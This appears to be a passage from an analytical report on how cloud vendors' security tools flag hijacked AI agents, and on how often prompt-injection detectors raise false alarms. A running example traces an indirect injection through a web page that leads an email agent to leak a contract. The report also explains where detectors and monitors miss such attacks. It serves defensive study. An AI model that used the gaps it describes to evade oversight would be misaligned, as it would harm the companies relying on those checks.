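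A Google Cloud list that includes later additions has 39 runtime detectors and 20 control-plane detectors. Some of the new detectors cover agents that grant or receive powerful roles, and others cover malicious skills. A skill is a package that gives an agent a new capability. The release notes define a malicious skill as a malicious binary that Google's threat intelligence has tagged as a skill. A skill that contains only harmful written instructions wouldn't meet that definition, although it could do as much damage.

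These detectors would probably have missed the email leak, because the agent started no unfamiliar program, touched no BigQuery or Cloud SQL data and used a mail tool it was allowed to use. Security researchers at Microsoft (2026) describe the general problem that an attacker who influences an agent's plans can cause harm without exceeding the agent's permissions. Google's service would have been much more likely to detect the attack if the hidden instructions had told an agent with shell access to open a reverse shell. A clean result from the service is therefore good evidence that no malicious program ran, but only weak evidence that no agent was hijacked.

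### Evaluation results

An evaluation scores an agent's runs on test cases or in live use. Developers have a rule, a person or another model do the scoring. Microsoft says an evaluation can measure the quality of a response, whether it is grounded in its source material, and whether the agent used its tools correctly.

A low score shows that the agent did badly by the chosen standard, but not why. An average score can also hide a single disastrous run, since one leak among ten thousand good answers barely changes it.

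In the email example, the result depends heavily on the standard used to judge the agent. The research agent could have scored well on groundedness, because its answer faithfully repeated what the page contained, including the attacker's instructions. A test of tool use would have been more helpful, because finding a supplier's delivery terms did not require searching for contracts or emailing one to a stranger. A model judging the whole trace might well have flagged those actions, but its input would also have included the attacker's text, which could contain instructions aimed at the judge.

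### Departures from normal behaviour

A system can also compare an agent's current behavior with its own past behavior. Microsoft recommends baselines for how often an agent calls each tool, how much material it retrieves, how many tokens it uses and how its evaluation scores are distributed.

The email leak might barely have changed any of these. A baseline of recipients would have worked better, since the agent had presumably never written to the attacker's address before, but it would also have raised an alert for every new customer.

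Defender has an alert for AI applications whose responses contain a type of sensitive information they haven't included before. The alert doesn't fire on new resources for a time, presumably because they have no history to compare against. It might also have missed the leak, because it checks the model's responses, and the model needed to write only the name of the file it was attaching, not the contents.

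Google's Agent Anomaly Detection goes beyond counting. Google Cloud's *Agent Anomaly Detection overview* describes three layers of analysis:

1. Statistical models and small machine-learning models pick out unusual sessions and discard much of the ordinary traffic.
2. A more thorough analysis examines the flagged sessions, decides whether each is a threat and explains its decision in words.
3. A final analysis looks at individual tool calls and their inputs.

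This could have caught the leak, because the product's definition of tool misuse includes indirect prompt injection. But the first layer would have had to flag the session as unusual. The analysis also runs separately from the agent to avoid slowing it down, so the email would probably have been sent before any verdict arrived.

The product needs traces that include the text of prompts and responses. It works only with Agent Runtime agents built with recent versions of Google's Agent Development Kit for Python. Customers have to request access and then enable it for each agent. Agents that don't meet the technical requirements don't appear in the product's list of agents, so a team could look at the list and wrongly conclude that every agent is covered.

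An anomaly shows that something changed. The cause may be an attack, a new version of the model or the end of the financial year. Microsoft says valid requests can trigger Defender's access anomaly alert if they differ enough from earlier ones.

### What Defender claims to cover and what it documents

Microsoft describes Defender's coverage of Foundry agents in two ways that don't fully match. *Extending Defender's AI Threat Protection to Microsoft Foundry Agents* (danielavillarreal, 2026) announced a public preview that covers seven threats: tool misuse, privilege compromise, resource overload, manipulation of the agent's goals, misaligned or deceptive behaviour, identity spoofing, and manipulation of the people who use the agent.

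Microsoft's reference page lists 12 alerts for these agents, all in preview:

- **Attacks on the model:** a blocked jailbreak, an unblocked jailbreak, and ASCII smuggling, which hides instructions in invisible characters.
- **Malicious links:** a phishing link in a user's prompt, a tool's output or the agent's response.
- **Suspicious access:** a request from a suspicious network address, from the anonymity network Tor, or from client software associated with attackers.
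- **Probing and overuse:** attempts to extract the agent's instructions, attempts to map its capabilities, and unusually high volumes of requests that could run up the bill.

Some of the seven threats clearly match a risk signal. High request volumes correspond to resource overload, jailbreaks correspond to manipulated goals, and phishing links in responses correspond to manipulated users. Suspicious access might indicate identity spoofing, but only indirectly.

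No alert on the agent list clearly corresponds to privilege compromise or deceptive behaviour. The only alert related to tool misuse flags a malicious link in a tool's output, which concerns what the tool returned, not what the agent did with it. The page also has an alert for "anomalous tool invocation", rated Low, but lists it under AI applications, which is surprising because calling tools is what distinguishes agents.

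Defender may detect more than this page documents. A later Microsoft overview mentions an extended set of alerts for Foundry agents but doesn't name them. Customers would be unwise to treat the seven claimed threats as covered until they can match each one to an alert. They can test this by staging an example of each threat and checking which alerts appear.

In the email example, the ASCII smuggling alert might have appeared if the attacker had used invisible characters. Instructions in white text on a white background would not have triggered it. An alert for a malicious link would have required a link that Microsoft already knew about.

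### Risks without a documented detector

OWASP's list of the ten main risks to agents is an independent standard for both companies. *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025) says the risks "are not theoretical" and names an example for six of the ten. One is EchoLeak, a case of goal hijacking in which hidden prompts made an AI assistant leak data.

The table compares the list with the two Google products and with Defender's 12 alerts for Foundry agents. Google itself links Agent Anomaly Detection to ASI02, ASI03, ASI08 and ASI10. The other matches are approximate.

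| OWASP risk | Google | Defender for Foundry agents |
|---|---|---|
| ASI01 Goal hijack | Indirect injection, under tool misuse | Jailbreaks, ASCII smuggling |
| ASI02 Tool misuse | Anomaly analysis, data exports | Malicious link in a tool's output only |
| ASI03 Identity and privilege abuse | Anomaly analysis, token and role detectors | Suspicious access only |
| ASI04 Supply chain | Malicious libraries and skills | Malicious link in a tool's output only |
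| ASI05 Unexpected code execution | Malicious scripts, reverse shells | None |
| ASI06 Memory and context poisoning | None for stored memory | None for stored memory |
| ASI07 Insecure communication between agents | None | None |
| ASI08 Cascading failures | Anomaly analysis | Unusual request volume only |
| ASI09 Exploitation of human trust | None | Phishing links only |
| ASI10 Rogue agents | Anomaly analysis | None |

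Neither company documents a detector for insecure communication between agents or for poisoned memory, even though danielavillarreal's own announcement warns that attackers can poison an agent's memory and OWASP cites an attack on Gemini's memory as an example. Exploitation of human trust is nearly as neglected. A polished but false explanation that persuades a manager to approve a payment is harder to match against a list than a phishing link.

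In each of these gaps, the harmful material can be ordinary text that becomes dangerous because of where it came from or which person or agent relies on it. A detector would need a record of the text's source, and for memory, that record would have to persist between sessions. Google's coverage is strongest for malicious programs and misused accounts, which security companies have been detecting for decades.

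The email leak is a goal hijack that passed from one agent to another. OWASP's short description of insecure communication mentions spoofed messages, but this message did come from the research agent, so a detector that verified only the sender would not have flagged it.

A platform may have undocumented detectors, and a risk without a detector may still have other defences. For example, developers can require approval for payments or refuse to store untrusted text in memory. But they can't infer from a dashboard with no alerts that these attacks aren't happening.

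### Quality problems and security problems

An agent that strays from its task may be badly prompted or hijacked, and the signal can be the same in both cases. Google's category of "rogue agents" includes any agent that deviates from its instructions, which either an attacker or contradictory instructions could cause. Google's category of cascading failures includes endless loops and repeated retries, which are often bugs.

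Microsoft's posture findings include a Medium severity rating for an agent without clear operational instructions, because it may expose data or respond inappropriately. Developers might see this as a prompt-writing problem rather than a security one. Microsoft's reasoning is sound but limited, since good instructions wouldn't stop an injection that the model follows anyway.

It helps to ask separately what happened and why. If the email agent sends a contract to a stranger, that is a security failure whether an attacker or a model error caused it, because the agent exceeded its authority. The cause still affects the repair. If the agent chose the wrong "Alex", the developer might make it confirm recipients. Limiting who the agent can write to would help against both mistakes and injections, so a developer can make that change before the cause is known.

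Alerts often suggest a cause more firmly than the evidence allows. Microsoft's reference page describes a malicious link in an agent's response as a sign that the agent is corrupted, but an email agent asked to summarise a phishing message might quote its link while working as intended. The page also states that a request from suspicious client software means the customer's resources "were likely compromised". However, *The Microsoft Defender for AI Alerts* (anas_hadidi, 2025) explains that the same alert doesn't necessarily mean a breach.

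For ASCII smuggling, anas_hadidi gives three possible causes: a malicious user, an innocent user who pasted text containing hidden characters, and a connected data source that added them. Blocking the user makes sense only in the first case. The alert's severity is Medium on anas_hadidi's Microsoft page but High on Microsoft's reference page.

A blocked injection attempt may need no repair, because the guardrail worked and the agent carried on or stopped safely. anas_hadidi still recommends further measures after a blocked jailbreak, including regular testing and tighter permissions. That is good general advice, but a developer who treated every blocked attempt as a new task would have little time for other work. Developers can learn more by looking at blocked attempts together. Twenty from the same supplier's website suggest that the site has been compromised and that the agent should stop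 reading it, since a later one might get through.

An alert can be correct even when there is no attacker. In a Microsoft workshop, participants deliberately trigger Defender alerts with a jailbreak attempt, a simulated phishing link and simulated suspicious client software. The right response to these alerts is to confirm that the test was planned and close them.

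## How signals reach developers on current platforms

A warning is more likely to change what a developer does (Premise 4) if it appears on a screen the developer already uses, with links to the evidence and to the setting that needs changing. Microsoft, Google, Amazon and Splunk each provide some of this. To compare them, suppose a company ran the email and research agents on each platform in turn, and a guardrail detected the hidden instructions on the supplier's web page. A second signal is the posture finding that the email agent can write to anyone without approval, which reaches the developer by a different route.

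Almost all public information about these products comes from the companies that sell them. There seems to be no independent evaluation of whether their screens get problems fixed sooner.

### Foundry's Operate and Compliance panes

Microsoft introduced Foundry Control Plane as a tool for developers, with security as one of its four pillars alongside controls, observability and fleet-wide operations. Developers open it by selecting Operate in the Foundry portal. Microsoft's documentation describes five panes. Overview shows the number of active agents, cost trends, the share of runs that finish and the behaviours the platform prevented. Assets lists the agents, models and tools across an Azure subscription, the unit Microsoft uses to group and bill a customer's cloud resources. Each entry shows a version, a cost, a health score and any alerts. Compliance covers guardrails and security, Quota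 covers capacity, and Admin covers user access.

The dashboard also displays alerts from Defender and from Purview, Microsoft's family of products for finding and protecting sensitive data. Microsoft claims that people can correlate these alerts with traces and evaluation results. A developer can open an agent's monitoring tab from the list of assets, but the overview doesn't describe a link from an alert to the run that caused it. The developer might have to find that run by when it happened.

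When a model's guardrails violate company policy, the Compliance pane offers a much shorter route from finding to fix, probably the shortest in any of the four products. If the company requires a prompt-injection check on every model and the research agent's model lacks one, the developer would see "Violations detected" next to the policy, according to Microsoft's compliance documentation. The developer would then compare the model's guardrail settings with the required ones and select "Fix now" to open those settings. The status updates within a few minutes after the developer saves the change. Anyone with access to the project can see the violation.

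Defender's posture findings take longer to act on. They appear on the Security posture tab with the affected resource and a risk level. Selecting one shows details and links for fixing the problem in the Azure portal, the separate website where customers manage their other Azure resources. A developer who had set up the email agent in Foundry would therefore leave Foundry to deal with a finding about it. That is still quicker than waiting for a ticket from the security team, but Oberoi had promised in the 2025 announcement that developers could act in the environment they already used.

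The hidden instructions on the web page might not produce a Defender alert. Microsoft's compliance documentation describes alerts for jailbreaks in user input, but these instructions arrive in a tool's response. A guardrail on tool responses could block them, and Microsoft lists indirect injection among the risks that Foundry's continuous evaluation can measure. The developer might then learn of the attack only from a guardrail event or a poor evaluation score.

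### Developers and analysts in Microsoft's design

Microsoft's announcements also describe Defender's deeper investigation features as tools for security staff. In June 2026 Microsoft wrote that analysts can use Defender to investigate agents through advanced hunting (searching detailed security records with written queries) and a map of how agents connect to one another across the network, though previews of these features were still to come. ITPro's *Microsoft unveils Foundry overhaul for managing, optimizing AI agents* had reported a similar split at launch, with developers controlling an agent's behaviour and lifecycle and IT teams enforcing security across the fleet.

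Dividing the work between developers and analysts is reasonable, since analysts are better placed to follow an intruder across systems. But a developer who sees an alert may still need an analyst to explain what caused it, which makes the promise of immediate context for developers less impressive.

Microsoft has built a more complete route for reporting flaws in ordinary code to developers. An integration between Defender and GitHub Code Security, generally available as of the June announcement, adds information from the live system to each vulnerability, such as whether the code is exposed to the internet or handles sensitive data. GitHub's Copilot can then generate, assign and check a fix.

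The nearest equivalent for agents is the process Brady describes for turning recurring failures into tested fixes. The Insights feature identifies the failures in an agent's traces, and the Agent Optimizer feature tests a possible fix against the version in use. Insights is generally available, but its connection to Agent Optimizer is in preview. Brady presents the benefits mainly as better quality and lower cost. Because the process begins with recurring failures, it would probably miss a leak that happened once, unless the developer turned that leak into a test.

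Other parts of the control plane are unfinished too. Microsoft (2026) listed tracing for agents hosted in Foundry as a preview in April, and Brady listed the Fleet and Operations features as public previews in November. Microsoft doesn't recommend previews for production workloads, so a company that followed this advice couldn't use some of Foundry's monitoring on the agents that attackers can reach.

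### Purview's warnings about sensitive data

The data-risk signals that Microsoft made generally available in June come from Purview. In Microsoft's example, an agent reveals sensitive financial data during testing. Purview flags this in real time and guides the developer to mask the data or restrict access to it before release.

Of Microsoft's signals, this warning best fits the case for telling developers directly, because the agent isn't live yet and the developer is already working on it and will probably have to fix the problem. But the email agent would trigger the warning only if a test made the agent handle sensitive material, so a team that tests with invented contracts might never see it.

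Even generally available signals may be off by default. Microsoft's compliance documentation still labelled the Purview integration a preview in May 2026, so some of its conditions may have changed since. Customers then needed a Purview licence, and someone with the Foundry Account Owner role had to turn the integration on for each subscription. The licence included audit records, but Microsoft charged for data security policies by usage. The integration also didn't yet support network isolation, which companies use to keep cloud services off the public internet.

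Those policies applied only to requests that carried a user's sign-in identity and went to Foundry's chat endpoint. Purview recorded and classified other interactions but did not enforce the policies on them. If the email agent had worked through the inbox at night under its own identity, Purview would have recorded its interactions for review the next morning but would not have blocked any of them.

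### The Security tab in Google's Agent Platform

An earlier Google page, Google Cloud's *View security and audit findings*, directs people to three places: Security Command Center for threats, Cloud Audit Logs for changes to permissions, and the logs of Model Armor, Google's guardrail service, for suspicious prompts and responses. Google has since added a Security tab to Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform, its service for building and running agents. Google Cloud's *View security findings* lists five widgets on the tab:

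- "AI risks by severity" ranks vulnerabilities, bad settings and dangerous combinations, such as an agent with high privileges and exposed data.
- "AI threats" shows critical and high-severity threat detections.
- "Agents with excessive permissions" lists access that agents have but don't use.
- "Compliance" compares the customer's deployments with security frameworks.
- "Content violations" counts breaches of content policy and charts them over time.

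If Model Armor recognised the hidden instructions, the count of content violations should rise. The developer could open the research agent's details page and select its Security tab to see only that agent's risks and violations. Clicking a metric on the main tab takes the developer out of the platform where the agent runs and into a filtered list in Security Command Center, the security team's console. Google's guide mentions no link from a finding to the agent's trace, so the developer would have to search separately for what the research agent passed on.

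Perhaps few customers can follow this route yet. The content widgets need Model Armor on an Agent Gateway, a feature in private preview. Without it, the dashboard hides them behind a banner, which is better than showing a zero that a developer could mistake for a sign that nothing is wrong. The other widgets show full information only with Security Command Center's Premium or Enterprise tier. Customers on the Standard tier can start a Premium trial from the tab with one click.

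A widget that shows only critical and high threats would leave out the BigQuery extraction that Google rates Low. Hiding minor findings reduces noise for developers, but it also hides any serious finding that is rated too low. Google also leaves agents out of its calculation of dangerous combinations until someone designates them as high-value resources, a step that a team could easily forget for a new agent.

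The permissions widget would probably not help with the email agent, because the widget looks for unused access to cloud resources. The agent's ability to email any address is a setting of its mail tool, which it uses every day. Google claims that the widget's details let customers remove permissions without breaking anything. That is likely true for most permissions, but one that looks unused might be one the agent needs only when it prepares the annual accounts.

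Google's "Remediate with Gemini" helps fix supported findings on resources that a company manages with Terraform, a tool that defines cloud infrastructure in text files. For other findings, Google provides guided snippets. It isn't clear that either would help a developer whose problem lies in an agent's instructions or in how one agent treats another's answers.

### Amazon's findings in Security Hub

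Amazon's customers can run agents on AgentCore, part of Amazon Bedrock. In Observer's *Amazon Security Chief Stephen Schmidt on What Customers Really Want* (2026), the Forrester analyst Madelein van der Hout says that AgentCore can give an agent its own identity, limit its access, apply policies to its actions and record what it does. Security findings go to a different product, Security Hub. AWS's monthly security news summary, *ICYMI* (2026), reports two additions to Security Hub in July 2026: GuardDuty AI Protection, which detects threats to AI services, and an inventory of AI resources across an organisation.

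GuardDuty AI Protection is generally available for Bedrock and for SageMaker, Amazon's machine-learning service, according to ERP Today's *AWS Security Hub's Azure Move Shows ERP Security Is Now Multi-Cloud*. It looks for unusual model use and for attackers who use stolen credentials to run models at the victim's expense. It analyzes CloudTrail, Amazon's log of account activity, and detects prompt-injection attempts through Bedrock's guardrails.

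If a Bedrock guardrail caught the hidden instructions, GuardDuty could raise a finding. According to AWS's *AI Inventory in Security Hub*, the inventory would then show the number of findings for AI resources that Amazon manages, including supported types from AgentCore. Opening one of these resources displays its configuration as JSON, but the guide describes no link to the agent's trace or to a fix. Unless AgentCore's own screens link to the trace, the developer would have to note the agent and the time of the finding, then search for the run in a monitoring tool.

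Amazon's descriptions of Security Hub don't suggest that developers will see security findings beside their traces. AWS's *Security Hub adds AI workload protection and multicloud support for Microsoft Azure* describes the product as a way to centralise security operations. AI Radar, which summarises Amazon's announcements, says Security Hub's inventory is for central security teams.

Developers may still be able to check the findings themselves. Ordinary member accounts can view the AI resources in that account, while administrator accounts can view the whole organisation's. If a company gives each team its own account, the email agent's developers could see only their own agents' finding counts, but they would need to know that the page exists and have a reason to visit it.

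AgentCore Evaluations, which Amazon introduced as a preview, is a more direct source of signals for developers. According to S&P Global (2026), it can check for unexpected or unauthorised behaviour as well as incorrect or unhelpful answers. A team could write its own evaluator to check whether the email agent had sent a document to a new address. The security problem would then show up as a failed test, which developers already know how to handle.

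Delta Air Lines went further and built its own gateway that can block traffic to an agent within seconds if the agent's evaluation scores cross a threshold, according to MarketBeat's *Amazon.com Unveils AI Agent Database Tools and Ops Agent at AWS re:Invent* (2026). Delta's chief architect described the gateway at Amazon's own conference, and MarketBeat's article gives no figures on how often it has blocked traffic or whether it was right to do so.

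The inventory has some large gaps. The only self-hosted agent it recognises is OpenClaw. An agent built with another framework on a company's own virtual machine wouldn't appear as an agent, although its calls to OpenAI or Anthropic might appear. Security Hub also reports no findings for self-hosted AI resources, so a lack of findings isn't evidence that such a resource is safe.

AI Radar reports that the inventory comes at no extra cost with Security Hub Essentials. SiliconANGLE (2026) describes monthly charges for virtual machines, container images, functions and identities. It isn't clear whether an agent's own identity would count towards the bill.

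### Splunk's traces with Cisco's findings

Splunk sells monitoring software that developers and operations staff use to find slow or failing services. Cisco, which owns Splunk, sells AI Defense, which checks the text going into and out of AI applications. Splunk's *Monitor security risks* describes how a customer can connect the two so that AI Defense's findings appear on the same pages as response times and errors.

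If AI Defense detected the hidden instructions, the developer could follow the signal in four steps:

1. A chart on the overview page shows an additional prompt-injection risk and whether AI Defense blocked it.
2. The agents page shows which application the risk belongs to.
3. The trace page lets the developer filter for prompt injection, open the affected run, and read the prompts, the responses and the actions that followed.
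4. Selecting the trace's identifier opens a map of the agents involved, where hovering over an item displays its risks.

The developer could then see the attacker's text and the email that followed it, if the trace had captured both. Microsoft, Google and Amazon do not document such a direct route from a finding to the run that triggered it. A developer might also notice a security risk while investigating a slow response, without opening a security page.

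The signals are less varied. The page lists prompt injection, code in an application's text, and three types of private data: personal, health and payment-card information. It includes no posture findings, so a developer wouldn't learn beforehand that the email agent could write to anyone. The page doesn't mention a link to the agent's settings. To change anything after finding the cause, the developer would have to go back to the platform where the team built the agent.

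Splunk explains that "No detected risks" may mean that nobody has connected the application to AI Defense. Checks that fail to run have their own label, but a developer may not be able to tell a clean result from no check at all.

Splunk has kept changing the product. In the May 2026 edition of *Monitor security risks*, Splunk labelled it an alpha feature, offered it without support, and asked readers to keep the documentation confidential. The November edition dropped that notice but gave no release status or licence terms. Splunk also switched from counting risks for each agent to counting them for each "agentic application". If the email and research agents belonged to one application, they would now share a row, and the developer would need the map to tell them apart.

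### The four designs compared

The table summarises the vendors' descriptions up to December 2026. "None described" means the vendor's guides to these screens mention no such link, although one may exist elsewhere in the product.

| | Microsoft Foundry | Google Agent Platform | Amazon Security Hub | Splunk with Cisco AI Defense |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Signals shown | Posture findings, guardrail violations, threat detections, data risks, evaluation results | Posture findings, threat detections, content violations | Finding counts for managed AI resources, threat detections | Prompt injection, code, private data |
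| Link to the trace | Microsoft claims correlation; no direct link from an alert described | None described | None described | Yes, down to the agent map |
| Link to the setting that fixes the cause | In Foundry for guardrails; through the Azure portal for Defender findings | Gemini fixes for some Terraform resources; snippets for other findings | None described in the AI inventory | None described |
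| Licence or plan | Defender plans for Defender signals; Purview licence for data risks | Security Command Center Premium or Enterprise for full information | Security Hub; GuardDuty for its threat detections | Connection to Cisco AI Defense; terms not stated |
| Release status | Insights and data-risk signals general; Fleet and Operations in preview | Tab not marked as a preview; Agent Gateway in private preview | AI Protection and AI inventory general | Alpha in May 2026; no status given in November |
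| Agents hosted elsewhere | Registration and Insights general; Defender posture for other platforms in preview | None described for the Security tab | OpenClaw on customers' own machines; a separate multi-cloud inventory in preview | Applications that send traces to Splunk |

All four vendors describe pages that someone has to open, and their guides to these pages don't mention sending a message to the person who built the agent. A developer who released the email agent in March and moved to another project has little reason to check its Security tab in June. Companies can probably set up notifications with other tools, but until they do, nobody may see a signal even if it appears on the right page.

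### Agents on other companies' platforms

A company also has to know which developer should receive a signal. ITPro's report on the launch of Foundry describes customers who have a thousand agents and don't know who created them. The problem gets harder when those agents run on several clouds. Each large vendor has an interest in hosting the customer's list of agents.

Microsoft offers developers and security teams separate routes for outside agents. Brady reports that developers can register these agents in Foundry, and that Insights can examine traces from agents built with LangGraph, LangChain and CrewAI. Both features are generally available. Security teams can use the preview that adds outside agents to Defender's inventory. According to Microsoft, the preview also provides posture findings for these agents and requires a connection through Agent 365. If the email agent ran on Bedrock,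 its developer might study its traces in Foundry while an analyst read its posture findings in Defender.

SiliconANGLE's *AWS previews a cloud-agnostic registry for managing agentic fleets at scale* (2026) reports on an Amazon registry, in preview since April, where developers can share agents, tools and skills. Amazon's Security Hub now checks Azure resources for bad settings and vulnerabilities, but the July announcement mentions AI Protection only for Amazon's own AI services.

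On 1 December 2026, Amazon announced three previews for Continuum, its automated security service, including one that looks for agents nobody has declared, according to Clubic's *AWS lâche les IA Mythos et GPT-6 Cyber sur les agents fantômes*. *AWS Opens a Gated Preview of Continuum for Agents Across Four Regions* (2026), a summary by the news aggregator AiSeek, adds that this preview searches Amazon's, Microsoft's and Google's clouds and reports how each agent is set up and what it may access. Customers don't have to register the agents or change their code. At the same conference, Amazon announced a service that gives every agent and subagent a verifiable identity, according to ITPro's *Trust and security top of mind* (2026). These identities could make it easier to match a finding to the right agent, at least on Amazon's cloud.

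These cross-cloud products mostly provide inventories and posture findings, which makes technical sense because a vendor can often read an agent's settings from outside if the customer grants access, but somebody has to record a trace while the agent is running. Van der Hout told Observer that large companies will need to govern their agents as one environment instead of through each vendor's control plane, and that she doesn't think the industry has fully solved this.

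### One vendor's suite or separate tools

The best argument for buying an integrated suite is that the platform running an agent also holds its settings, which lets Foundry take a developer from a guardrail violation to the relevant control. A separate monitoring tool has only the data the agent sends it, and usually can't change the agent. A suite also takes less work to set up. Security Hub, for example, finds supported AgentCore resources without extra configuration. A vendor that controls both the agent platform and the detector can also update both together when trace field names change.

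For a small team with all its agents on one platform, those advantages probably outweigh the drawbacks. But the products in these suites are not fully integrated. Developers move from Foundry to the Azure portal, or from Google's Security tab to Security Command Center, and they may need a separate licence to see anything in the second product.

Dependence on one vendor also creates security risks. If the vendor's detector misses an attack, the customer may have no other detector to catch it, and an outage could disable the agent's controls and alerts at the same time. daily.dev's summary of a CSO Online report on Security Hub mentions analysts' warnings about single points of failure, gaps between products and lock-in. Van der Hout argues that when Amazon or another large cloud provider supplies the infrastructure, the agent runtime and the security controls, customers still need a way to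 test that the controls work.

Separate tools that share open standards would address these problems. A company could send its traces to any monitoring tool that accepts OpenTelemetry, and collect findings in the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework, a common format for security data that Security Hub also uses. The company could replace a weak detector without losing its traces, or run two detectors and compare them. Its developers could also keep the monitoring tool they already know, which is an advantage if Premise 4 is true.

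Splunk and Cisco show how useful the result can be, but they are an imperfect example because Cisco owns Splunk. With unrelated vendors, the customer would have to make sure that each finding includes the correct trace identifier, and keep that working as both products change. This could require regular updates because OpenTelemetry's names for agent data are still under development. The customer would also have to build the final step, from the trace to the agent's settings.

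A company can show different signals in different places. It makes sense to show posture findings in the agent platform, since the evidence and the fix are both in the agent's settings. Guardrail events and threat detections are more useful next to a trace. A company with agents on several platforms has good reason to keep its traces in a portable format.

Before choosing a platform, a company can run a fairly cheap test. Someone puts a harmless hidden instruction on a web page that a test agent will read, and a developer who doesn't know about the test starts work as usual. The company records whether the developer notices the security signal, how long they take to find the instruction and its source, and how many products and access requests they need to go through to reach the setting that would have blocked it.

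## How often signals are wrong, and when to alert or block

Attacks are rare compared with harmless runs, so even a detector that makes few mistakes can produce mostly false alarms. Whether signals are right often enough to deserve attention (Premise 2) therefore depends on the detector, how common attacks are, and what a signal triggers. Wrongly blocking an agent interrupts its work, which may do much less harm than taking up a person's time with a false alert.

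### Why a good detector can raise mostly false alarms

A detector's detection rate is the share of attacks it flags, and its false alarm rate is the share of harmless runs it flags. Its precision is the share of its alerts that are real attacks. Precision matters most to a developer deciding whether to open an alert, but researchers usually report the other two rates because precision depends on how common attacks are.

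Suppose a company's agents complete 100,000 runs a day and attackers target 10 of them. A detector catches 90% of the attacks and flags 1% of the harmless runs, which gives 9 true alerts and about 1,000 false ones:

precision = 9 / (9 + 1,000) ≈ 0.9%

A developer would have to open about 112 alerts to find one attack. Catching every attack would barely help, since only 10 of 1,010 alerts, or 1%, would be true. Cutting the false alarm rate to 0.01% would leave about 10 false alerts and raise precision to 9/19, or about 47%. *AI-Driven Security Alert Screening and Alert Fatigue Mitigation in Security Operations Centers* (2026), a survey, credits Axelsson with formalising this problem two decades ago and still lists it among the main causes of alert fatigue.

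Many detectors check each tool output separately, so a quoted false alarm rate may also apply to single outputs rather than whole runs. If a detector wrongly flags 1% of harmless outputs, and its errors are independent, it will flag almost 10% of harmless runs that contain ten outputs.

### Measured error rates of prompt-injection detectors

*Passing the Test You Trained On* (Liu, 2026) tested 15 detectors on the kind of text that agents read. The text came from the benchmarks AgentDojo, which simulates office, banking, travel and messaging tasks, and τ-bench, which simulates customer service for a retailer and an airline. Liu first ran the correct tool calls for each task with no attack present, so any flag was a false alarm. Liu then planted attacks, repeated the calls and labelled every output that had changed as an attack. For comparison, the paper used BIPIA, a benchmark that hides attacks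 in emails, tables and answers to coding questions.

The table shows six of the detectors. The false alarm columns use each detector's default threshold, the score above which it flags a text. The detection columns use a threshold that gives 1% false alarms on the same benchmark.

| Detector | Harmless AgentDojo outputs flagged | Harmless AgentDojo tasks stopped | Attacks caught, AgentDojo | Attacks caught, τ-bench | Attacks caught, BIPIA |
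|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Horizon-Labs | 0.0% | 0.0% | 82.2% | 100.0% | 37.7% |
| Wolf Defender | 0.9% | 3.1% | 73.8% | 90.8% | 3.5% |
| Prompt Guard 2 (86M) | 0.6% | 2.1% | 69.4% | 57.9% | 10.4% |
| Prismor | 6.5% | 17.5% | 72.2% | 15.2% | 4.0% |
| PIGuard | 29.5% | 59.8% | 2.1% | 52.7% | 95.1% |
| ProtectAI v2 | 30.1% | 69.1% | 0.5% | 10.1% | 0.7% |

The 15 detectors had false alarm rates ranging from zero to over 90%. PIGuard gave its maximum score to a banking tool's message that a password had been updated. A company that chose PIGuard for its excellent BIPIA result would have stopped more than half of the harmless AgentDojo tasks at the default setting and missed nearly every attack at the stricter setting.

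PIGuard's training data, which included 1,116 BIPIA inputs, explains much of this. The data also included 53 of the 62 attack texts that Liu planted in τ-bench, but only as short prompts. When those attacks appeared inside tool outputs, PIGuard caught 52.1% of the ones it had trained on and 55.8% of the others. Horizon-Labs was trained on documents and tool responses with planted instructions, and it did best on both agent benchmarks, although Liu found none of the benchmarks' attacks in the training data he checked. Detectors seem to work best on text in the same form as their training data, so a company should test them on its own agents' tool outputs.

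Even the best results don't show that a detector could reach the 0.01% false alarm rate in the example. Liu had only 339 harmless outputs from AgentDojo and 1,533 from τ-bench. A detector with no false alarms in 339 outputs could still raise false alarms on nearly 0.9% of harmless outputs. Showing with 95% confidence that the rate is below 0.01% would take about 30,000 harmless outputs with no false alarms. *PVDetector* (2026) set its threshold for at most 1% false alarms using just 100 harmless queries. A threshold chosen that way could easily flag 2% or 3% of later harmless traffic.

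Rates measured on fixed test sets can also overstate how well a detector performs against attackers who adapt to it. Liu could not include closed commercial detectors, which would include Microsoft's Prompt Shields, so his results don't show how often Foundry customers' alerts are wrong.

Some harmless text is especially likely to cause false alarms. *PIDS-Bench* (Shire and Kim, 2026) tested a detector that scored above 0.98 out of 1 on F1, a measure that combines precision and detection rate, but still flagged about a third of harmless prompts on security-related topics. Shire and Kim chose these prompts to provoke mistakes, so the everyday rate should be lower, though an email agent at a software company might read security-related text all day. No threshold on any of the three detectors they trained gave both an F1 of at least 0.95 and a false alarm rate of 10% or less on the harmless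 security-related prompts.

Better training data can reduce false alarms. *Prompt Injection Detection for Email Agents Through Attack Chain Modeling* (2026) describes a detector that flagged 65.2% of harmless prompts containing words typical of attacks. Adding such prompts to its training data cut the figure to 0.6%. Raising the threshold instead cut false alarms to about 5%, but the detector then caught only 36.9% of BIPIA attacks. However, Shire and Kim found that this kind of training fixed false alarms mainly on prompts similar to the added ones. Most false alarms on prompts from other sources remained.

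Combining detectors can also increase false alarms. For web agents, *WAInjectBench* (2025) found that a combination caught more of some attacks than the best single detector, but its false alarm rate was nearly the sum of the individual rates. *Securing AI Agents Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) reports that a layered defence wrongly filtered or further checked 5.7% of legitimate retrievals, and calls this acceptable for most applications. That may be true if a false alarm only triggers another automatic check. But if each of the 100,000 daily runs in the example retrieved one document, and every false alarm went to a developer, developers would receive 5,700 false alarms a day.

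### Detectors that judge what the agent does

A detector can examine the agent's actions instead of the text the agent reads. This works badly if the detector lacks the details that distinguish harmful actions from harmless ones. *Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* (2026) describes a test on harmless sessions in which agents recalled a fact from memory and emailed it to a team. The detector flagged 76–100% of these sessions for some models and none for others, depending on whether the model tended to retrieve from memory before sending. A real leak through memory involves the same two steps and differs only in the recipient's address, which the detector ignored by design.

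Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that has more information. Before Claude Code runs a command that could do damage, the classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, including their inputs. It doesn't read tool outputs, so instructions hidden on a web page can't reach it directly. It also doesn't read the agent's explanations, because they might lead it to approve a dangerous action.

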